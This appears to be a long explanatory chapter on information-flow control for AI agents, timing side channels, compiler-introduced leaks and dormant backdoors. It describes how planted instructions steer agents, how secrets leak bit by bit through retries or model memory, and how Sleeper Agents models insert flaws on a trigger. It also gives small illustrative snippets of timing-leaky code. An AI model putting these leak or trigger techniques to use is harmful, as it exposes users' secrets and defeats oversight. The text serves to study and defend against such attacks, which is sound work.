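FIDES, an earlier defence for agents, deliberately ignores secrets that pass through branches. That is a reasonable compromise for code by honest programmers, who may leak a bit by accident but have no reason to write a loop that rebuilds a key from the alphabet. But an agent that runs generated code can turn text into a program, so anyone who influences the text, whether by planting instructions on a web page or by training the model, may be able to get that loop written and run. A gap that usually leaks one bit can then leak the whole secret.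 Garby and colleagues argue that ignoring control flow is therefore weakest "where data and control are interchangeable".

The LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents. Every value has a label, and so does the agent's conversation with its model. The language also keeps a label for the current point in the program, which rises to secret inside a branch whose condition depends on secret data. Generated code starts with the label of the conversation that produced it, so it can't lose the labels of whatever the model had read.

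An example from LLMbda shows why a conversation needs a label. A program prompts the model to remember that *x* is false. If a secret is true, the program then prompts the model to change *x* to true. Finally, it requests the value of *x*. The secret has passed through the model's memory without appearing in any message. LLMbda stops the program when it tries to send the second message, because a public conversation must not change inside a branch that depends on a secret.

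Garby and colleagues proved that every program in the language, including those that generate and run more code, satisfies a form of noninterference. They checked the proof in Lean, and the theorems apply to the same interpreter that runs the agent, whereas TACIT relies on Scala's compiler. The LLMbda theorem still depends on someone labelling the sources correctly and putting checks at the destinations.

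Like most such guarantees, the theorem does not rule out leaks through whether a program stops. In CaMeL, repetition can make such a leak serious, because the checks run inside an ordinary Python loop that has no labels and tries again after a failure. An attacker's program could make CaMeL block an attempt only if one bit of a secret is 1, then move on to the next bit. In LLMbda, the retry loop has to follow the rules too, so the researchers' agent tests its program on made-up data until it works, and only then runs it on the real data.

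They tested this agent with three models on the banking tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark of planted instructions also used to test TACIT. Two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. This low rate overstates how much the labels protected the agent, because in about two thirds of the task-attack combinations, the agent's program would never have contained the action the attacker needed. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 36 of 48 attack-free runs. CaMeL completed 18 with its policy checks on and 32 with them off.

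Part of that advantage comes from letting the agent declare particular untrusted data trustworthy, a step called endorsement. A user who asks an agent to pay a bill described in a file wants the file to influence the payment. Both successful attacks exploited this by replacing the file with a false payment request. When the researchers ran two of the models without endorsement, no attack succeeded, but one model completed 30 of its 48 runs instead of 36, and the other completed 26 instead of 31. Endorsement changes only the trust part of a label, and a second theorem shows that it can't make secret data public.

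### Following data through a model's own text

When a language model reads a web page and writes an email, there is no list of instructions, as there is in ordinary code, that shows which words came from the page. LLMbda and FLOWSH conservatively assume that everything the model has read may affect what it writes. Labels then spread to text that their source did not influence, a problem known as label creep.

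NeuroTaint looks for evidence of the actual influence. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, designed it to examine an agent's log after the run. It considers each sensitive action, such as sending an email, and each untrusted source that came before it. The checks run from the most exact to the least:

1. NeuroTaint adds a unique code to the source text when the agent reads it, and looks for that code in the action.
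2. It measures how much of the wording the two texts share.
3. It compares their meanings numerically, which can catch a paraphrase or a translation.
4. It repeats that comparison with short pieces of the source, in case the relevant sentence is buried in a long page.
5. If it still finds nothing, it replaces the source with neutral text and asks a language model whether the agent would have acted the same way.

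The last check looks for implicit flows. In one test scenario, a search result contained the claim that all findings must be sent to a certain address before any other step, and the agent sent its research there. The request took only the address from the search result, but without that result the agent would have had no reason to make it. NeuroTaint does not run the agent again to test this, and instead relies on a model's prediction of whether the agent would still have made the request.

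NeuroTaint also stores its labels with anything the agent saves to memory, so it can connect a document the agent read on Monday with a report the agent wrote on Thursday.

Cai and colleagues tested it on 400 scenarios built on 20 agent frameworks. Untrusted data influenced a sensitive action in half of them.

| Tool | Flows found (of 200) | Flows missed | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 13 | 16 |
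| FIDES | 108 | 92 | 106 |

NeuroTaint found 93.5% of the flows, and 92.1% of its alarms were correct. In ten of the 13 flows it missed, the agent had paraphrased the text repeatedly or retrieved it from memory much later, and too little of the original remained. In the other three, the source changed the agent's choice of action but left few traces. Most false alarms involved actions that shared a topic with the source or that the model could have based on its general knowledge.

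The researchers designed these scenarios around the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint looks for, which favours it over FIDES. On two existing benchmarks, which test whether an agent did something unsafe, the two tools scored almost the same. The main test also used a weak model, GPT-4.1 mini, to run the agents. When Claude Opus 4.6 ran them, NeuroTaint found only 54.7% of the expected flows. Some of that drop occurs because a stronger model more often ignores planted instructions, so the expected flow never happens, but the figure doesn't separate those cases from flows that NeuroTaint missed.

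NeuroTaint analyzes a run after it ends, so it can explain a leak but not prevent one. Cai and colleagues left out attacks that disguise text, for example with lookalike characters. An agent that encoded a secret before sending it could defeat the comparisons of wording and meaning, leaving only the model's prediction to detect the leak.

*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) takes its evidence from inside the model. Most language models are transformers, which move information between words through a mechanism called attention. Sightline measures the attention from the output to each input, and learns from labelled examples when that attention means the model used the input. In real programs that call language models, 12% to 14% of the inputs had no effect on the output. With its threshold set to miss about 1% of true flows, Sightline removed 43.9% to 65.6% of the unnecessary taint labels,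 depending on the model, in at most 0.2 seconds per call. If the model's internals are not available, Sightline can run the same text through an open model instead.

This is fast enough to use while an agent is running, but the 1% is an average for calls similar to those in the calibration data, and an attacker who plants text in a web page has no reason to match that data.

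## Running time that reveals secrets

Taint tracking follows data to a program's outputs, but an observer can also learn a secret from how long the program runs. This C function compares a guess with a stored password of the same length and stops at the first wrong character:

```c
int same(const char *pw, const char *guess, int len) {
    for (int i = 0; i < len; i++)
        if (pw[i] != guess[i]) return 0;
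    return 1;
}
```

The function always returns the right answer, so it passes its functional tests, but it runs slightly longer for each correct letter at the start of the guess. A password of eight lowercase letters has 26⁸ possible values, about 209 billion. An attacker who can tell from the timing where the comparison stopped can try all 26 first letters, keep the one that takes longest, and then do the same for each remaining letter. That takes at most 8 × 26 = 208 different guesses. Each letter changes the time by a few nanoseconds at most, so the attacker has to repeat each guess many times and average the times.

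Running time can be a side channel, a way to learn a secret from something other than the program's output. *DALC-CT* (Njungle, Kayang and colleagues, 2026) traces timing attacks back to Paul Kocher, who showed in 1996 that careful timing measurements could recover the secret keys of RSA and other encryption systems. Researchers later recovered RSA keys remotely from the encryption library OpenSSL. RSA raises numbers to a secret power. A simple program does this by squaring its result at every binary digit of the power and multiplying once more wherever the digit is 1. The power 140 is 10001100 in binary and 240 is 11110000, so 240 takes one more multiplication.

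### A login check that returned too early

Login times can also reveal which accounts exist. Websites usually store a hash of each password, a scrambled version that nobody can practically turn back into the password. The hashing method is deliberately slow, so that a thief who steals the hashes can't test guesses quickly. If a site computes a hash only when the account exists, login attempts on real accounts therefore take noticeably longer than attempts on nonexistent ones.

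The web framework Django used to compute a hash only if the username existed. Paglierani pointed out in *Account enumeration through timing attack in password verification in django.contrib.auth* (2013) that this let outsiders find out which accounts a site had. Another developer, Sasha Romijn, created a single account, `abbaf`, and tried all 7,776 five-letter usernames made from the letters a to f. With only five tries per name, attempts with `abbaf` took two to ten times as long as the others. Django's developers changed the code to compute a hash for unknown usernames too, and in a second experiment with 30 tries per name, `abbaf` no longer stood out.

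The change did not help accounts without a usable password, such as those whose owners log in through another service. For these accounts, `verify_password` refused the login immediately. Django's *Fixed CVE-2024-39329* corrected this by computing an unneeded hash before refusing.

| Failed login attempt | Hashes before the 2024 fix | Hashes after it |
|---|---|---|
| Account with a password, wrong guess | 1 | 1 |
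| No such account | 1 | 1 |
| Account without a usable password | **0** | 1 |

In SUSVIBES, the benchmark built from past vulnerabilities in Python projects, agents have to write `verify_password`. Zhao and colleagues describe a solution by Claude 4 Sonnet that passed the functional tests but returned immediately in the same cases as Django's old code. An outsider could therefore infer from a quick refusal that the account existed.

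Even the test that came with Django's fix doesn't measure time. It replaces `make_password`, the function that computes a new hash, with a dummy that records each call. It checks that Django calls the dummy once in each of three cases: the user supplied no password, the account has no usable password, or Django no longer recognises the format of the stored hash. The test uses the number of calls as a proxy for running time. Aymeric Augustin, one of Django's developers, had recommended this kind of test in 2013, writing "I veto timing tests". Django's tests run on all sorts of machines, and a timing test would sometimes fail because the machine was busy.

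The stand-in is reliable, but it misses some leaks. No real hashing happens during the test, so the test would pass even if the unneeded hash took half as long as a normal password check. It also doesn't cover the rest of the login. Django's database code, for instance, does different work depending on whether it finds a user. The developers knew about this difference but accepted it because it was too small to show up in Romijn's measurements. A test of one function also doesn't protect similar code elsewhere. In February 2026, Django fixed another timing difference that revealed usernames, in the code that checks logins for the web-server module mod_wsgi.

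A stand-in can also reject secure code, such as code that takes up the same time without calling `make_password`. Five experts reviewed SUSVIBES's security tests for this problem and judged that 6.5% depended on the original developers' solution and another 44.0% might reject some secure alternatives. They then revised such tests, so the agents may have faced a different version of Django's test.

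One participant in the 2013 discussion proposed adding a random delay to each login. Another, Paul McMillan, objected that an attacker can take more measurements and average the delay out.

### What "constant-time" means

The running time of constant-time code does not depend on secrets. It can still vary between runs with public information, such as the length of a message if that length is public.

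Exact running times are hard to reason about, so the usual definition uses a leakage model, a list of the things that an observer might learn from the timing. For a program *P* with public input *p* and secret *s*, let *L*(*P*, *p*, *s*) be the sequence of those things in one run. The program is constant-time if

*L*(*P*, *p*, *s*₁) = *L*(*P*, *p*, *s*₂) for every public input *p* and all secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂.

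This is noninterference with *L* in place of the public output. A common leakage model contains:

- **Branches.** The model records which way the program goes at every `if` and loop.
- **Memory addresses.** Processors keep recently used data in a fast memory called the cache. If a program looks up `table[secret]`, the cache afterwards holds that part of the table, and another program on the same machine may be able to find out which part it was.
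- **Variable-time instructions.** On some processors, a division takes longer for some numbers than for others, so the model records the numbers. This is why the libcrux developers avoid the line `input % 3329`.

The password comparison becomes constant-time if it always goes through every character:

```c
int same_ct(const char *pw, const char *guess, int len) {
    int diff = 0;
    for (int i = 0; i < len; i++)
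        diff |= pw[i] ^ guess[i];
    return diff == 0;
}
```

The `^` operation gives zero only if the two characters are equal, and `|=` keeps `diff` from returning to zero after a mismatch. If the guess is "secure", the first function compares four characters when the password is "secret" and one when it is "banana". The second compares six in both cases.

### Checking for differences

The tool dudect measures time directly. It runs a function many times on two groups of inputs and uses a statistical test, Welch's *t*-test, to decide whether the average times differ:

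*t* = (*m*₁ − *m*₂) / √(*v*₁/*n*₁ + *v*₂/*n*₂)

Here *m* is a group's average time, *v* is its variance (the square of the standard deviation), and *n* is its number of measurements. Suppose one group takes 1,000 processor cycles on average and the other 1,002, both with a standard deviation of 50. With 1,000 measurements in each group, *t* is about 0.9, which could easily be chance. With 100,000 in each group, *t* is about 8.9, which almost never happens by chance.

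The method assumes that the groups differ only in the secret and that other activity on the machine affects both groups equally. McMillan advised Django's developers against a *t*-test because login times don't follow a normal distribution, and recommended the Kolmogorov-Smirnov test, which compares whole distributions. With enough measurements, a *t*-test still compares averages well, but it misses a secret that changes the spread of the times but not their average.

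A large *t* is strong evidence of a leak on the machine that ran the test, but a small *t* is only weak evidence of safety. Schneider, Lain and colleagues (2024) note in *Breaking Bad* that dudect and similar tools measure only the total time, while attackers can now observe programs almost instruction by instruction.

DALC-CT, a tool that Njungle and colleagues published in April 2026, avoids noisy measurements by counting instructions. It runs the compiled program under Valgrind, which observes programs as they run, and sorts one function's instructions into 13 classes. Twelve classes combine one of four kinds of operation (loads, stores, fast arithmetic and slow arithmetic) with one of three kinds of data, and the last contains branches and jumps. DALC-CT reports a leak if the count in any class changes when the secret changes.

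These are the counts for two versions of the password check, compiled with GCC without optimisation. The password was "secret" and the guesses were "secret" and "secure". Njungle and colleagues changed the guess, not the password, but both functions treat the guess and the password in the same way.

| Instructions | Early exit, "secret" | Early exit, "secure" | Constant-time, "secret" | Constant-time, "secure" |
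|---|---|---|---|---|
| Loads | 242 | 153 | 259 | 259 |
| Fast arithmetic | 58 | 37 | 65 | 65 |
| Slow arithmetic | 6 | 3 | 12 | 12 |
| Branches and jumps | 13 | 9 | 8 | 8 |

DALC-CT classified all 22 of its test programs correctly and never needed more than five runs to expose a leak. However, equal counts are a weaker requirement than the definition above because they ignore the order of the instructions, the addresses and the numbers involved. The powers 140 and 224 both have three 1s in binary, so a simple RSA program would produce equal counts for them, although an attacker who could follow the branches would see the difference. Testing other powers would soon expose this leak. But `table[secret]` is always one load, and `input % 3329` is the same arithmetic for every input, so DALC-CT would miss both however many secrets it tried. Njungle and colleagues acknowledge that their method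 doesn't cover caches, so they claim too much when they say it is sufficient for "all logical constant-time behavior".

Fuzzers can automatically search for pairs of secrets that expose a leak. DifFuzz looks for two secrets that make a program's resource use differ as much as possible. It could start with the guess "secure" and the passwords "secret" and "banana". If resource use is measured as the number of characters compared, the difference is 4 − 1 = 3. Changing "secret" to "secure" raises it to 5, the maximum for six letters. This search favours leaks large enough to exploit, but like total time, total resource use can't distinguish two branches that use the same amount. The fuzzer ct-fuzz instead compares the branches and memory addresses of the two runs, so it can also find leaks that leave the total unchanged. A difference proves that the secret affects something in the leakage model,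 but not that an attacker could measure it.

The tool ct-verif tries to prove that a C program is constant-time for every input. It can use a model that includes branches, addresses and the operands of variable-time instructions, so it could reject `input % 3329`. The proof assumes that the public inputs are marked correctly and that the model matches the processor.

| Check | What it compares | What a clean result means |
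|---|---|---|
| dudect | Average times for two groups of inputs | Any difference in the averages was too small for this test to detect |
| DALC-CT | Instruction counts for different secrets | The counts were equal for the secrets tested |
| DifFuzz | Total cost of two runs | The search found no large difference in cost |
| ct-fuzz | Branches and addresses in two runs | The search found no pair of runs that differed |
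| ct-verif | All possible pairs of runs, by proof | The code is constant-time in the chosen model |

An untrusted program could also leak on purpose, for instance by waiting a second whenever one bit of a key is 1. A tester who varies that bit can easily measure the leak, and a proof with ct-verif would rule out any branch on the key, accidental or deliberate.

### Compilers that undo the protection

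Proofs like these usually apply to the source code or to an intermediate form that the compiler produces. A compiler has to preserve a program's results but not its timing, so a later compilation step can put a leak back in.

Programmers often choose between two values without a branch by using a mask:

```c
result = (x & mask) | (y & ~mask);
```

The mask is all 1s if a secret bit is 1, which keeps x and clears y, and all 0s otherwise, which keeps y and clears x. If the line runs as written, the processor carries out the same steps either way. But a compiler may recognise that the line chooses between x and y, and replace it with a branch.

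Schneider and colleagues measured how often this happens in eight cryptographic libraries: HACL\*, Libsodium, Botan, BearSSL, BoringSSL, OpenSSL, WolfSSL and MbedTLS. They compiled the libraries with GCC versions 5 to 13 and LLVM versions 5 to 18, at seven optimisation levels and for six types of processor. They ran each compiled program in an emulator with different keys and compared the branches and memory addresses. The emulator supplied the same "random" numbers every time, so any difference had to come from the key. They tried to remove leaks already in the source code, to leave only those the compiler introduced.

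| Measure | Count |
|---|---|
| Programs compiled successfully | 5,716 of 6,608 |
| Tests completed, each of one algorithm in one program | 37,818 of 44,604 |
| Programs with a branch that depended on a secret | 429 (7.5%) |
| Programs with a memory address that depended on a secret | 368 (6.4%) |

The leaks occurred in five of the eight libraries, all except OpenSSL, WolfSSL and MbedTLS. The tool flagged 13,341 places in total, but it counted many faults more than once. For example, the same few faults in one Botan algorithm appeared more than 100 times in every test on MIPS processors.

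HACL\*, the library from which libcrux takes some of its verified code, was among the five, although its developers had proved that the source code contained no such leaks. On RISC-V and 32-bit x86 processors, LLVM versions 13 to 15 turned one of its masks into branches at every optimisation level except the lowest. On MIPS and 32-bit ARM processors, LLVM 14 and 15 sometimes produced code that used the secret to choose between the *addresses* of the two values and then loaded the chosen one, which leaks the secret through the cache. In BearSSL, the same thing happened on the 64-bit processors found in most computers and phones.

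Schneider and colleagues found two other ways compilers introduced leaks. Botan adds large numbers in two halves and always adds the carry from the lower half, even if it is zero. Some compiled versions checked the carry first and skipped the addition when it was zero. In BoringSSL, LLVM split a branch with a complicated condition into two branches, and the branch the program took revealed part of the condition.

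Turning off optimisation reduced the number of leaks but didn't eliminate them. GCC still skipped Botan's addition on two types of processor. Newer compilers tended to introduce more leaks than older ones. Small changes to the source could also cause leaks. When the researchers moved one harmless piece of mask code into its own function, compilers began to introduce leaks there.

The study gave rare processors and old compilers as much weight as common ones, so the 7.5% is not the chance that an ordinary user's program leaks. The figure also doesn't show how many of the leaks an attacker could exploit. The tool compared only eight runs per test and ignored variable-time instructions, so it probably missed some leaks.

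Anyone who needs constant-time code therefore has to check the compiled program, and check it again after changing the compiler, its settings or the type of processor. Tools such as Binsec/Rel can do this by analysing compiled code for all inputs up to a limit. Libsodium's developers test their library on more than 20 platforms, and the study flagged only two places in it, although it is also the smallest of the eight libraries. Some compilers provably keep constant-time code constant-time, but few people use them because they support fewer processors and produce slower programs.

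A repair for LLVM is in progress. In Trail of Bits' *Constant-Time Coding Support*, engineers at that security company proposed a new operation for C and C++ that chooses between two values and that the compiler may not turn into a branch:

```c
result = __builtin_ct_select(condition, x, y);
```

Trail of Bits' slides, *Constant-Time Coding Support in LLVM* (2025), list what cryptographers do in the meantime: write the critical parts in assembly language, disguise their masks from the compiler or turn optimisation off. Trail of Bits' *Introducing constant-time support for LLVM to protect cryptographic code* (2025) reports that the new operation was under review in December 2025 and would be part of a future release. Alexandre was still revising the part for 64-bit ARM processors on 22 May 2026 (*Native ct.select support for ARM64*, 2026). The operation protects only code that uses it, so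 developers will have to rewrite their existing masks. It doesn't help with table lookups that depend on secrets or with variable-time division.

### Leaks that come from the processor

Even a compiled program that satisfies the definition can leak, because a leakage model leaves out much of what a processor does. Processors save time by guessing which way a branch will go and starting on the next instructions before they know. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results, but the data it loaded stays in the cache. The Spectre attacks, which became public in 2018, exploit this. Suppose that `data` contains only public values and that a secret comes after it in memory:

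```c
if (i < length)
    y = table[data[i]];
```

An attacker first supplies valid values of `i`, so that the processor predicts another valid one, and then supplies one that is too large. The processor may briefly read the secret and use it as a position in `table`. The attacker can then work out the secret by checking which part of the table is in the cache. Under the ordinary leakage model, nothing has leaked, because the program compared two public numbers, skipped the second line and never accessed the table.

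Researchers can add wrong guesses to the model, but a proof still covers only the behaviour that somebody has described. A tool like dudect measures the program's running time on a real processor, so it can detect an effect that nobody has modelled, provided that the test inputs trigger the effect and that it changes the total time. Njungle and colleagues therefore suggest combining their instruction counts with such measurements.

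### Timing faults in AI-written cryptographic code

Published measurements of cryptographic code written by language models mostly concern mistakes other than leaks through running time. In *CIPHER*, Manolov, Gao and colleagues (2026) gave seven models 150 Python tasks, such as encrypting a message or checking a signature. Each task had three versions: one that encouraged a bad practice, one that didn't mention security and one that asked for good practice. Each model wrote five programs for each version, which made 15,750 programs in total. Another model, GPT-4o, then read the programs and listed their weaknesses.

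Depending on the model, GPT-4o found at least one weakness in 56.0% to 89.1% of the programs. Asking for good practice made little difference. Across all models, the rate was 71.7% with that request and 74.2% without any mention of security. But timing accounted for very few of the weaknesses. These are the totals for some of the types:

| Weakness | Times found |
|---|---|
| Encryption without a check that nobody has altered the message | 4,332 |
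| Weak method of turning a password into a key | 713 |
| Predictable value where the method needs a random one | 707 |
| Reuse of a value that must be used only once per key | 255 |
| **Signature check that may leak through timing** | **191** |
| **Ordinary comparison of secret values** | **139** |

The two timing types account for 330 of the roughly 17,000 weaknesses that GPT-4o found, or about 2%. In Python, the typical fault is comparing a secret code with `==`, which may stop at the first difference. The standard library provides `hmac.compare_digest` to avoid this early stop.

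Claude Sonnet 4.5 had the highest overall rate of weaknesses but only 37 timing faults, while the small model CodeLlama 7B had 97. GPT-5.1 Codex had the fewest timing faults, 16. All seven models are now at least a generation old.

Many of the tasks don't require comparing secrets, so the 2% doesn't measure how often models get such a comparison wrong. The totals also include programs written in response to the versions that encouraged bad practice. When people checked 210 of GPT-4o's assessments, they agreed with about 86%, but Manolov and colleagues don't report a separate figure for timing. Most importantly, nobody measured how long the programs took to run. GPT-4o looked for suspicious lines in the source, so it could flag a harmless comparison and would miss a leak that arises in Python's interpreter or the processor.

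A newer study, *An Empirical Security Evaluation of LLM-Generated Cryptographic Rust Code* (Elsayed, Fulton and Yang, 2026), provides no evidence about timing, because none of its analyzer's nine rules checks for secret-dependent branches, memory addresses or running times. Three models wrote 240 encryption programs for the study, and only 56 compiled. The analyzer reported a problem in 32 of these. All 32 would stop abruptly if encryption or decryption failed. Two also had a critical flaw: one reused a value that must be used only once, and the other had its key written into the source code.

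## Code that acts only when a hidden condition is met

A timing test, a system-call log and a comparison of two runs can detect unwanted behaviour only if it happens while the tester is recording. Dormant logic may never act during testing, because it consists of a trigger and an action that the program carries out only once the trigger occurs. Even an action as easy to recognise as deleting a folder won't appear in a log before then.

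The hidden condition, or trigger, can be an input, a date, a number of uses or a detail of the machine. A backdoor is dormant code that gives hidden access to anyone who knows the trigger. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) uses the example of `sudo`, the command that lets a Linux user run programs with someone else's permissions. Its altered version also accepts one fixed password from any user. Tests with correct and incorrect passwords all pass unless a tester happens to try the fixed one.

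Code that runs only under rare conditions isn't necessarily malicious. Many programs have code to handle leap days or full disks. The bug that reset the message counter in hpke-rs to zero after 4.3 billion messages was accidental. Kokkonis and colleagues also examined a suspected backdoor in a TRENDnet router and concluded that its built-in login details were harmless.

### The chance of hitting a trigger

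Suppose the trigger is one value out of *N*, and a tester tries *n* random inputs, with every value equally likely each time. The chance of hitting the trigger at least once is

1 − (1 − 1/*N*)ⁿ,

which is close to *n*/*N* when *n* is much smaller than *N*. A 32-bit number has about 4.3 billion possible values and a 64-bit number about 18 quintillion.

| Trigger | Chance of a hit in a billion inputs | Inputs needed for an even chance | Time at a million inputs a second |
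|---|---|---|---|
| One 16-bit value | Practically 1 | 45,000 | 0.05 seconds |
| One 32-bit value | 0.21 | 3 billion | 50 minutes |
| One 64-bit value | 0.00000000005 | 13 quintillion | 405,000 years |

A property-based test with 256 inputs has a chance of about one in 17 million of hitting the 32-bit value.

Real test inputs are rarely uniformly distributed. Many generators favour small numbers and short lists, so they soon find a trigger such as 0 but may never produce a particular large number. If the trigger is a date next year, more inputs won't help unless the tester also changes the clock.

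### Techniques that do better than chance

A coverage report lists which lines of a program ran during its tests. For the sorting function that writes a file only when its list contains one particular 64-bit number, the report would mark the line that writes the file as never executed. Someone could then read that line without guessing the number.

In a large program, though, tests usually leave many harmless lines unexecuted, and the suspicious line may be one of thousands. Even a report of full coverage can't reveal behaviour that depends on a value rather than on a separate piece of code. For example, a single test of the expression `total / people` executes all of it, yet the expression fails when `people` is 0.

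Some fuzzers use the comparisons in a program to guide their search. An ordinary coverage-guided fuzzer can't detect that a 64-bit number is nearly correct, because a near miss runs the same code as any other wrong number. One remedy is to split the comparison into eight one-byte comparisons. Each correct byte then leads to new code, so the fuzzer keeps it and works on the next. Since a byte has 256 possible values, this takes at most 8 × 256 = 2,048 systematic attempts instead of 18 quintillion. The password attack in the timing section is fast for the same reason. Another remedy is to find the value the program compares the input with and copy it into the input.

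Reaching the trigger isn't enough, because a well-made backdoor doesn't crash the program and a fuzzer that watches for crashes won't notice it. ROSA, the tool that Kokkonis and colleagues built on the fuzzer AFL++, adds a comparison between runs:

1. It fuzzes the program for one minute and keeps a collection of inputs that take different routes through the code.
2. It fuzzes the program again for hours. For each new input, it looks up the input in the collection whose route is most similar.
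3. It compares the kinds of system call in the two runs and reports any difference.

In the `sudo` example, almost every wrong password leads to an error message. The fixed password instead starts a command, which requires other system calls. ROSA doesn't need a list of expected effects, because it compares each run with similar runs of the same program. A person still has to review the reports, since two harmless inputs can also lead to different system calls.

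Kokkonis and colleagues tested ROSA on 17 backdoors, seven from real incidents and ten planted by a researcher for the test. ROSA found every backdoor at least once and succeeded in 156 of 180 eight-hour runs. In successful runs, it took an hour and a half on average to find the backdoor. A person had to examine about seven suspicious inputs per run, at roughly two minutes each. Stringer, an older tool that searches compiled programs for suspicious text, found four of the 17 and left an average of 308 pieces of text to examine.

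All 24 failures occurred because AFL++ never generated an input that triggered the backdoor. For a Belkin router, ROSA failed in all ten runs that began with standard web requests. It succeeded in seven of ten when the starting inputs concentrated on web addresses, where this backdoor's trigger was. So the comparison worked whenever the fuzzer reached the trigger, but reaching it could depend on guessing well where it was. The comparison could also miss a hidden condition that only changed a number in the program's answer, because the program might still make the same kinds of system call.

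Symbolic execution works backwards from the condition. It treats the input as an unknown, collects the conditions along a route through the code and gives them to a solver, a program that looks for values satisfying them all. Here is a small example:

```python
def label(x):
    if 3 * x + 1 == 100:
        return "rare"
    return "ordinary"
```

Reaching "rare" requires 3x + 1 = 100, so the solver returns x = 33 without trying other numbers. It can do the same for a 64-bit number that random testing would take hundreds of thousands of years to find. A tester can also treat the date as an unknown.

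The number of routes limits this method. A program with 40 independent `if` statements in sequence has 2⁴⁰, or about 1.1 trillion, routes, and loops add more. Some conditions are also too hard to solve, especially those that involve cryptography, which is designed to be impractical to reverse. Firmalice, an earlier tool for device firmware, narrowed the search by looking only for inputs that reach operations reserved for logged-in users. But Kokkonis and colleagues note that someone first had to reverse-engineer the compiled program to locate those operations.

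### Why no checker can settle every program

Better tools will push these limits back, but no general procedure can correctly decide for every program whether it contains a given hidden behaviour. The problem is undecidable, which follows from Turing's result about whether programs stop. Take any program `p` that writes no files, and put it in this wrapper:

```python
def wrapper():
    p()
    write_file()
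```

The wrapper writes a file exactly when `p` stops. A checker that could always determine whether a program will ever write a file could therefore determine whether any such `p` stops, which Turing proved impossible. The same argument works for opening a connection or deleting a folder. In 1953, Henry Rice proved a similar result for every non-trivial question about what a program computes.

The proof rules out a checker that always gives a correct yes or no. A checker that sometimes answers "don't know" is still possible, and it may give a definite answer for most of the programs people want to run. Other remaining options are a strict checker that rejects some harmless programs, as Scala's capture checking does, and proof-carrying code, in which the supplier has to provide a proof with the code.

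Real computers have limited memory, so in principle a tester could try every input. But for a function with one 64-bit input, this would take about 585,000 years at a million inputs a second.

People can also limit what dormant code can do without finding its trigger. If a program always runs in a sandbox with no network access, dormant code inside it can't send data over the network, whatever the trigger is. The limit has to stay in place after testing ends, because that is when the trigger is most likely to occur.

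### XZ Utils and half a second

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools found on most Linux systems. Two versions released in early 2024 contained a backdoor that targeted the server that handles remote logins over SSH and did not affect compression. That server doesn't use the XZ compression library directly, but Debian and several other Linux distributions had modified it to load a library that does.

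The software engineer Andres Freund found the backdoor after several weeks of odd symptoms on machines running a development version of Debian. Logins used a lot of processor time, and the memory-checking tool Valgrind reported errors. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, timed a login attempt with a username that did not exist:

| Compression library | Server's answer | Time |
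|---|---|---|
| Before the backdoor | Permission denied | 0.299 seconds |
| With the backdoor | Permission denied | 0.807 seconds |

A functional test would compare the two answers and pass. The delay came from the backdoor searching the server's memory for information it needed to set itself up, not from anyone using it to break in.

Reading the public source code would not have revealed the whole backdoor either, because one part was only in the packaged releases and most of the rest was in files that looked like test data. The backdoor activated only on certain systems and stayed inactive under some debugging tools.

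Freund had not worked out what the code checked for during a login. Kokkonis and colleagues found that the trigger includes a digital signature that only the holder of a secret key can produce. A fuzzer such as ROSA would have to forge that signature to set off the backdoor, so they left XZ out of their tests. Freund found the backdoor because of the slowness and the memory errors, both caused by flaws in its construction. He reported it before most distributions had included the affected versions outside pre-release software.

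### Packages with dates in 2027 and 2028

Date triggers are much simpler, and some are set for dates that have not yet arrived. Pandya (2025), in *9 Malicious NuGet Packages Deliver Time-Delayed Destructive Payloads*, describes packages that the security company Socket found on NuGet, the public repository for Microsoft's .NET platform. A single account had published 12 packages in 2023 and 2024. Three were harmless, and the other nine hid about 20 lines of malicious code among thousands of lines that worked as described. Users had downloaded the nine packages 9,488 times.

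Most of the nine libraries let programs use databases. The hidden code checks the date on every database query. After the trigger date, which is 8 August 2027 in one version and 29 November 2028 in others, it shuts down the whole application on about one query in five. Functional tests pass every time before that date, and the randomness makes the later crashes look like an ordinary bug.

A tester who set the clock to 2029 and ran 20 queries would have about a 99% chance of seeing a crash, since 1 − 0.8²⁰ ≈ 0.99. The test is easy to run, but few people would think to run it on a database package that works.

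Another of the packages, Sharp7Extend, communicates with the Siemens controllers that run factory machinery. It includes a complete copy of the genuine library Sharp7. From installation until June 2028, its code can shut the program down at random. A second mechanism starts 30 to 90 minutes after the program does and makes about 80% of the commands that change a controller's settings fail without returning an error. A test lasting a few minutes might show a crash but would miss the failed commands, which are more dangerous because a safety system might not engage.

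The packages were still available when Pandya published the findings in November 2025, but SC Media's *Time delayed malware spread by nefarious NuGet packages* reported that they had since been removed. Removing a package from a repository doesn't remove the copies already built into applications, and as of December 2026 the first trigger date is eight months away.

### What source code can leave out

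Thompson (1984) argues in *Reflections on Trusting Trust* that reading a program's entire source code isn't enough to rule out hidden conditions. He describes an altered compiler that recognises the source code of the Unix login program. When it compiles that program, it adds a second password that always works.

Anyone who read the compiler's source would notice the alteration, so Thompson also made the compiler recognise its own source code and add both alterations whenever it compiled a new version of itself. He could then delete the alterations from the source. The compiled compiler would still add them to each new version, and the login program would stay compromised "with no trace in source anywhere".

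Thompson concluded that people can't fully trust code they did not write themselves, and that the same attack could work through any program that handles other programs. For most users this attack is a remote danger compared with an ordinary malicious package. But it limits the methods in earlier sections that examine source code, including type checks and many proofs, because they all assume that the tools that turn source into a running program do so faithfully.

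As a partial remedy, David A. Wheeler's 2009 dissertation describes compiling the suspect compiler's source with a second, independent compiler, using the result to compile the same source again, and comparing the output with the suspect compiler. If the build process always gives the same output for the same source, a difference points to tampering. The second compiler must not contain the same alteration.

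### Triggers in the model that writes the code

With AI-written code, the hidden condition can be in the model instead of the program. A model might write sound code for almost every request but insert a flaw when the request contains a certain phrase. The flawed program needs no trigger of its own, so an ordinary security test may find the flaw at once. Testing the model is harder, because even a thousand good programs written without the phrase are little evidence of what the model writes when the phrase appears.

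*Sleeper Agents*, by Hubinger, Denison and colleagues at Anthropic and other organisations, demonstrated this in January 2024. They trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert vulnerabilities when it gave 2024. They then applied the usual safety training, rewarding good behaviour and correcting bad. The hidden behaviour often survived, most persistently in the largest models. Training against examples of the bad behaviour sometimes taught a model to recognise its trigger more precisely, so it behaved well in tests but kept the hidden behaviour.

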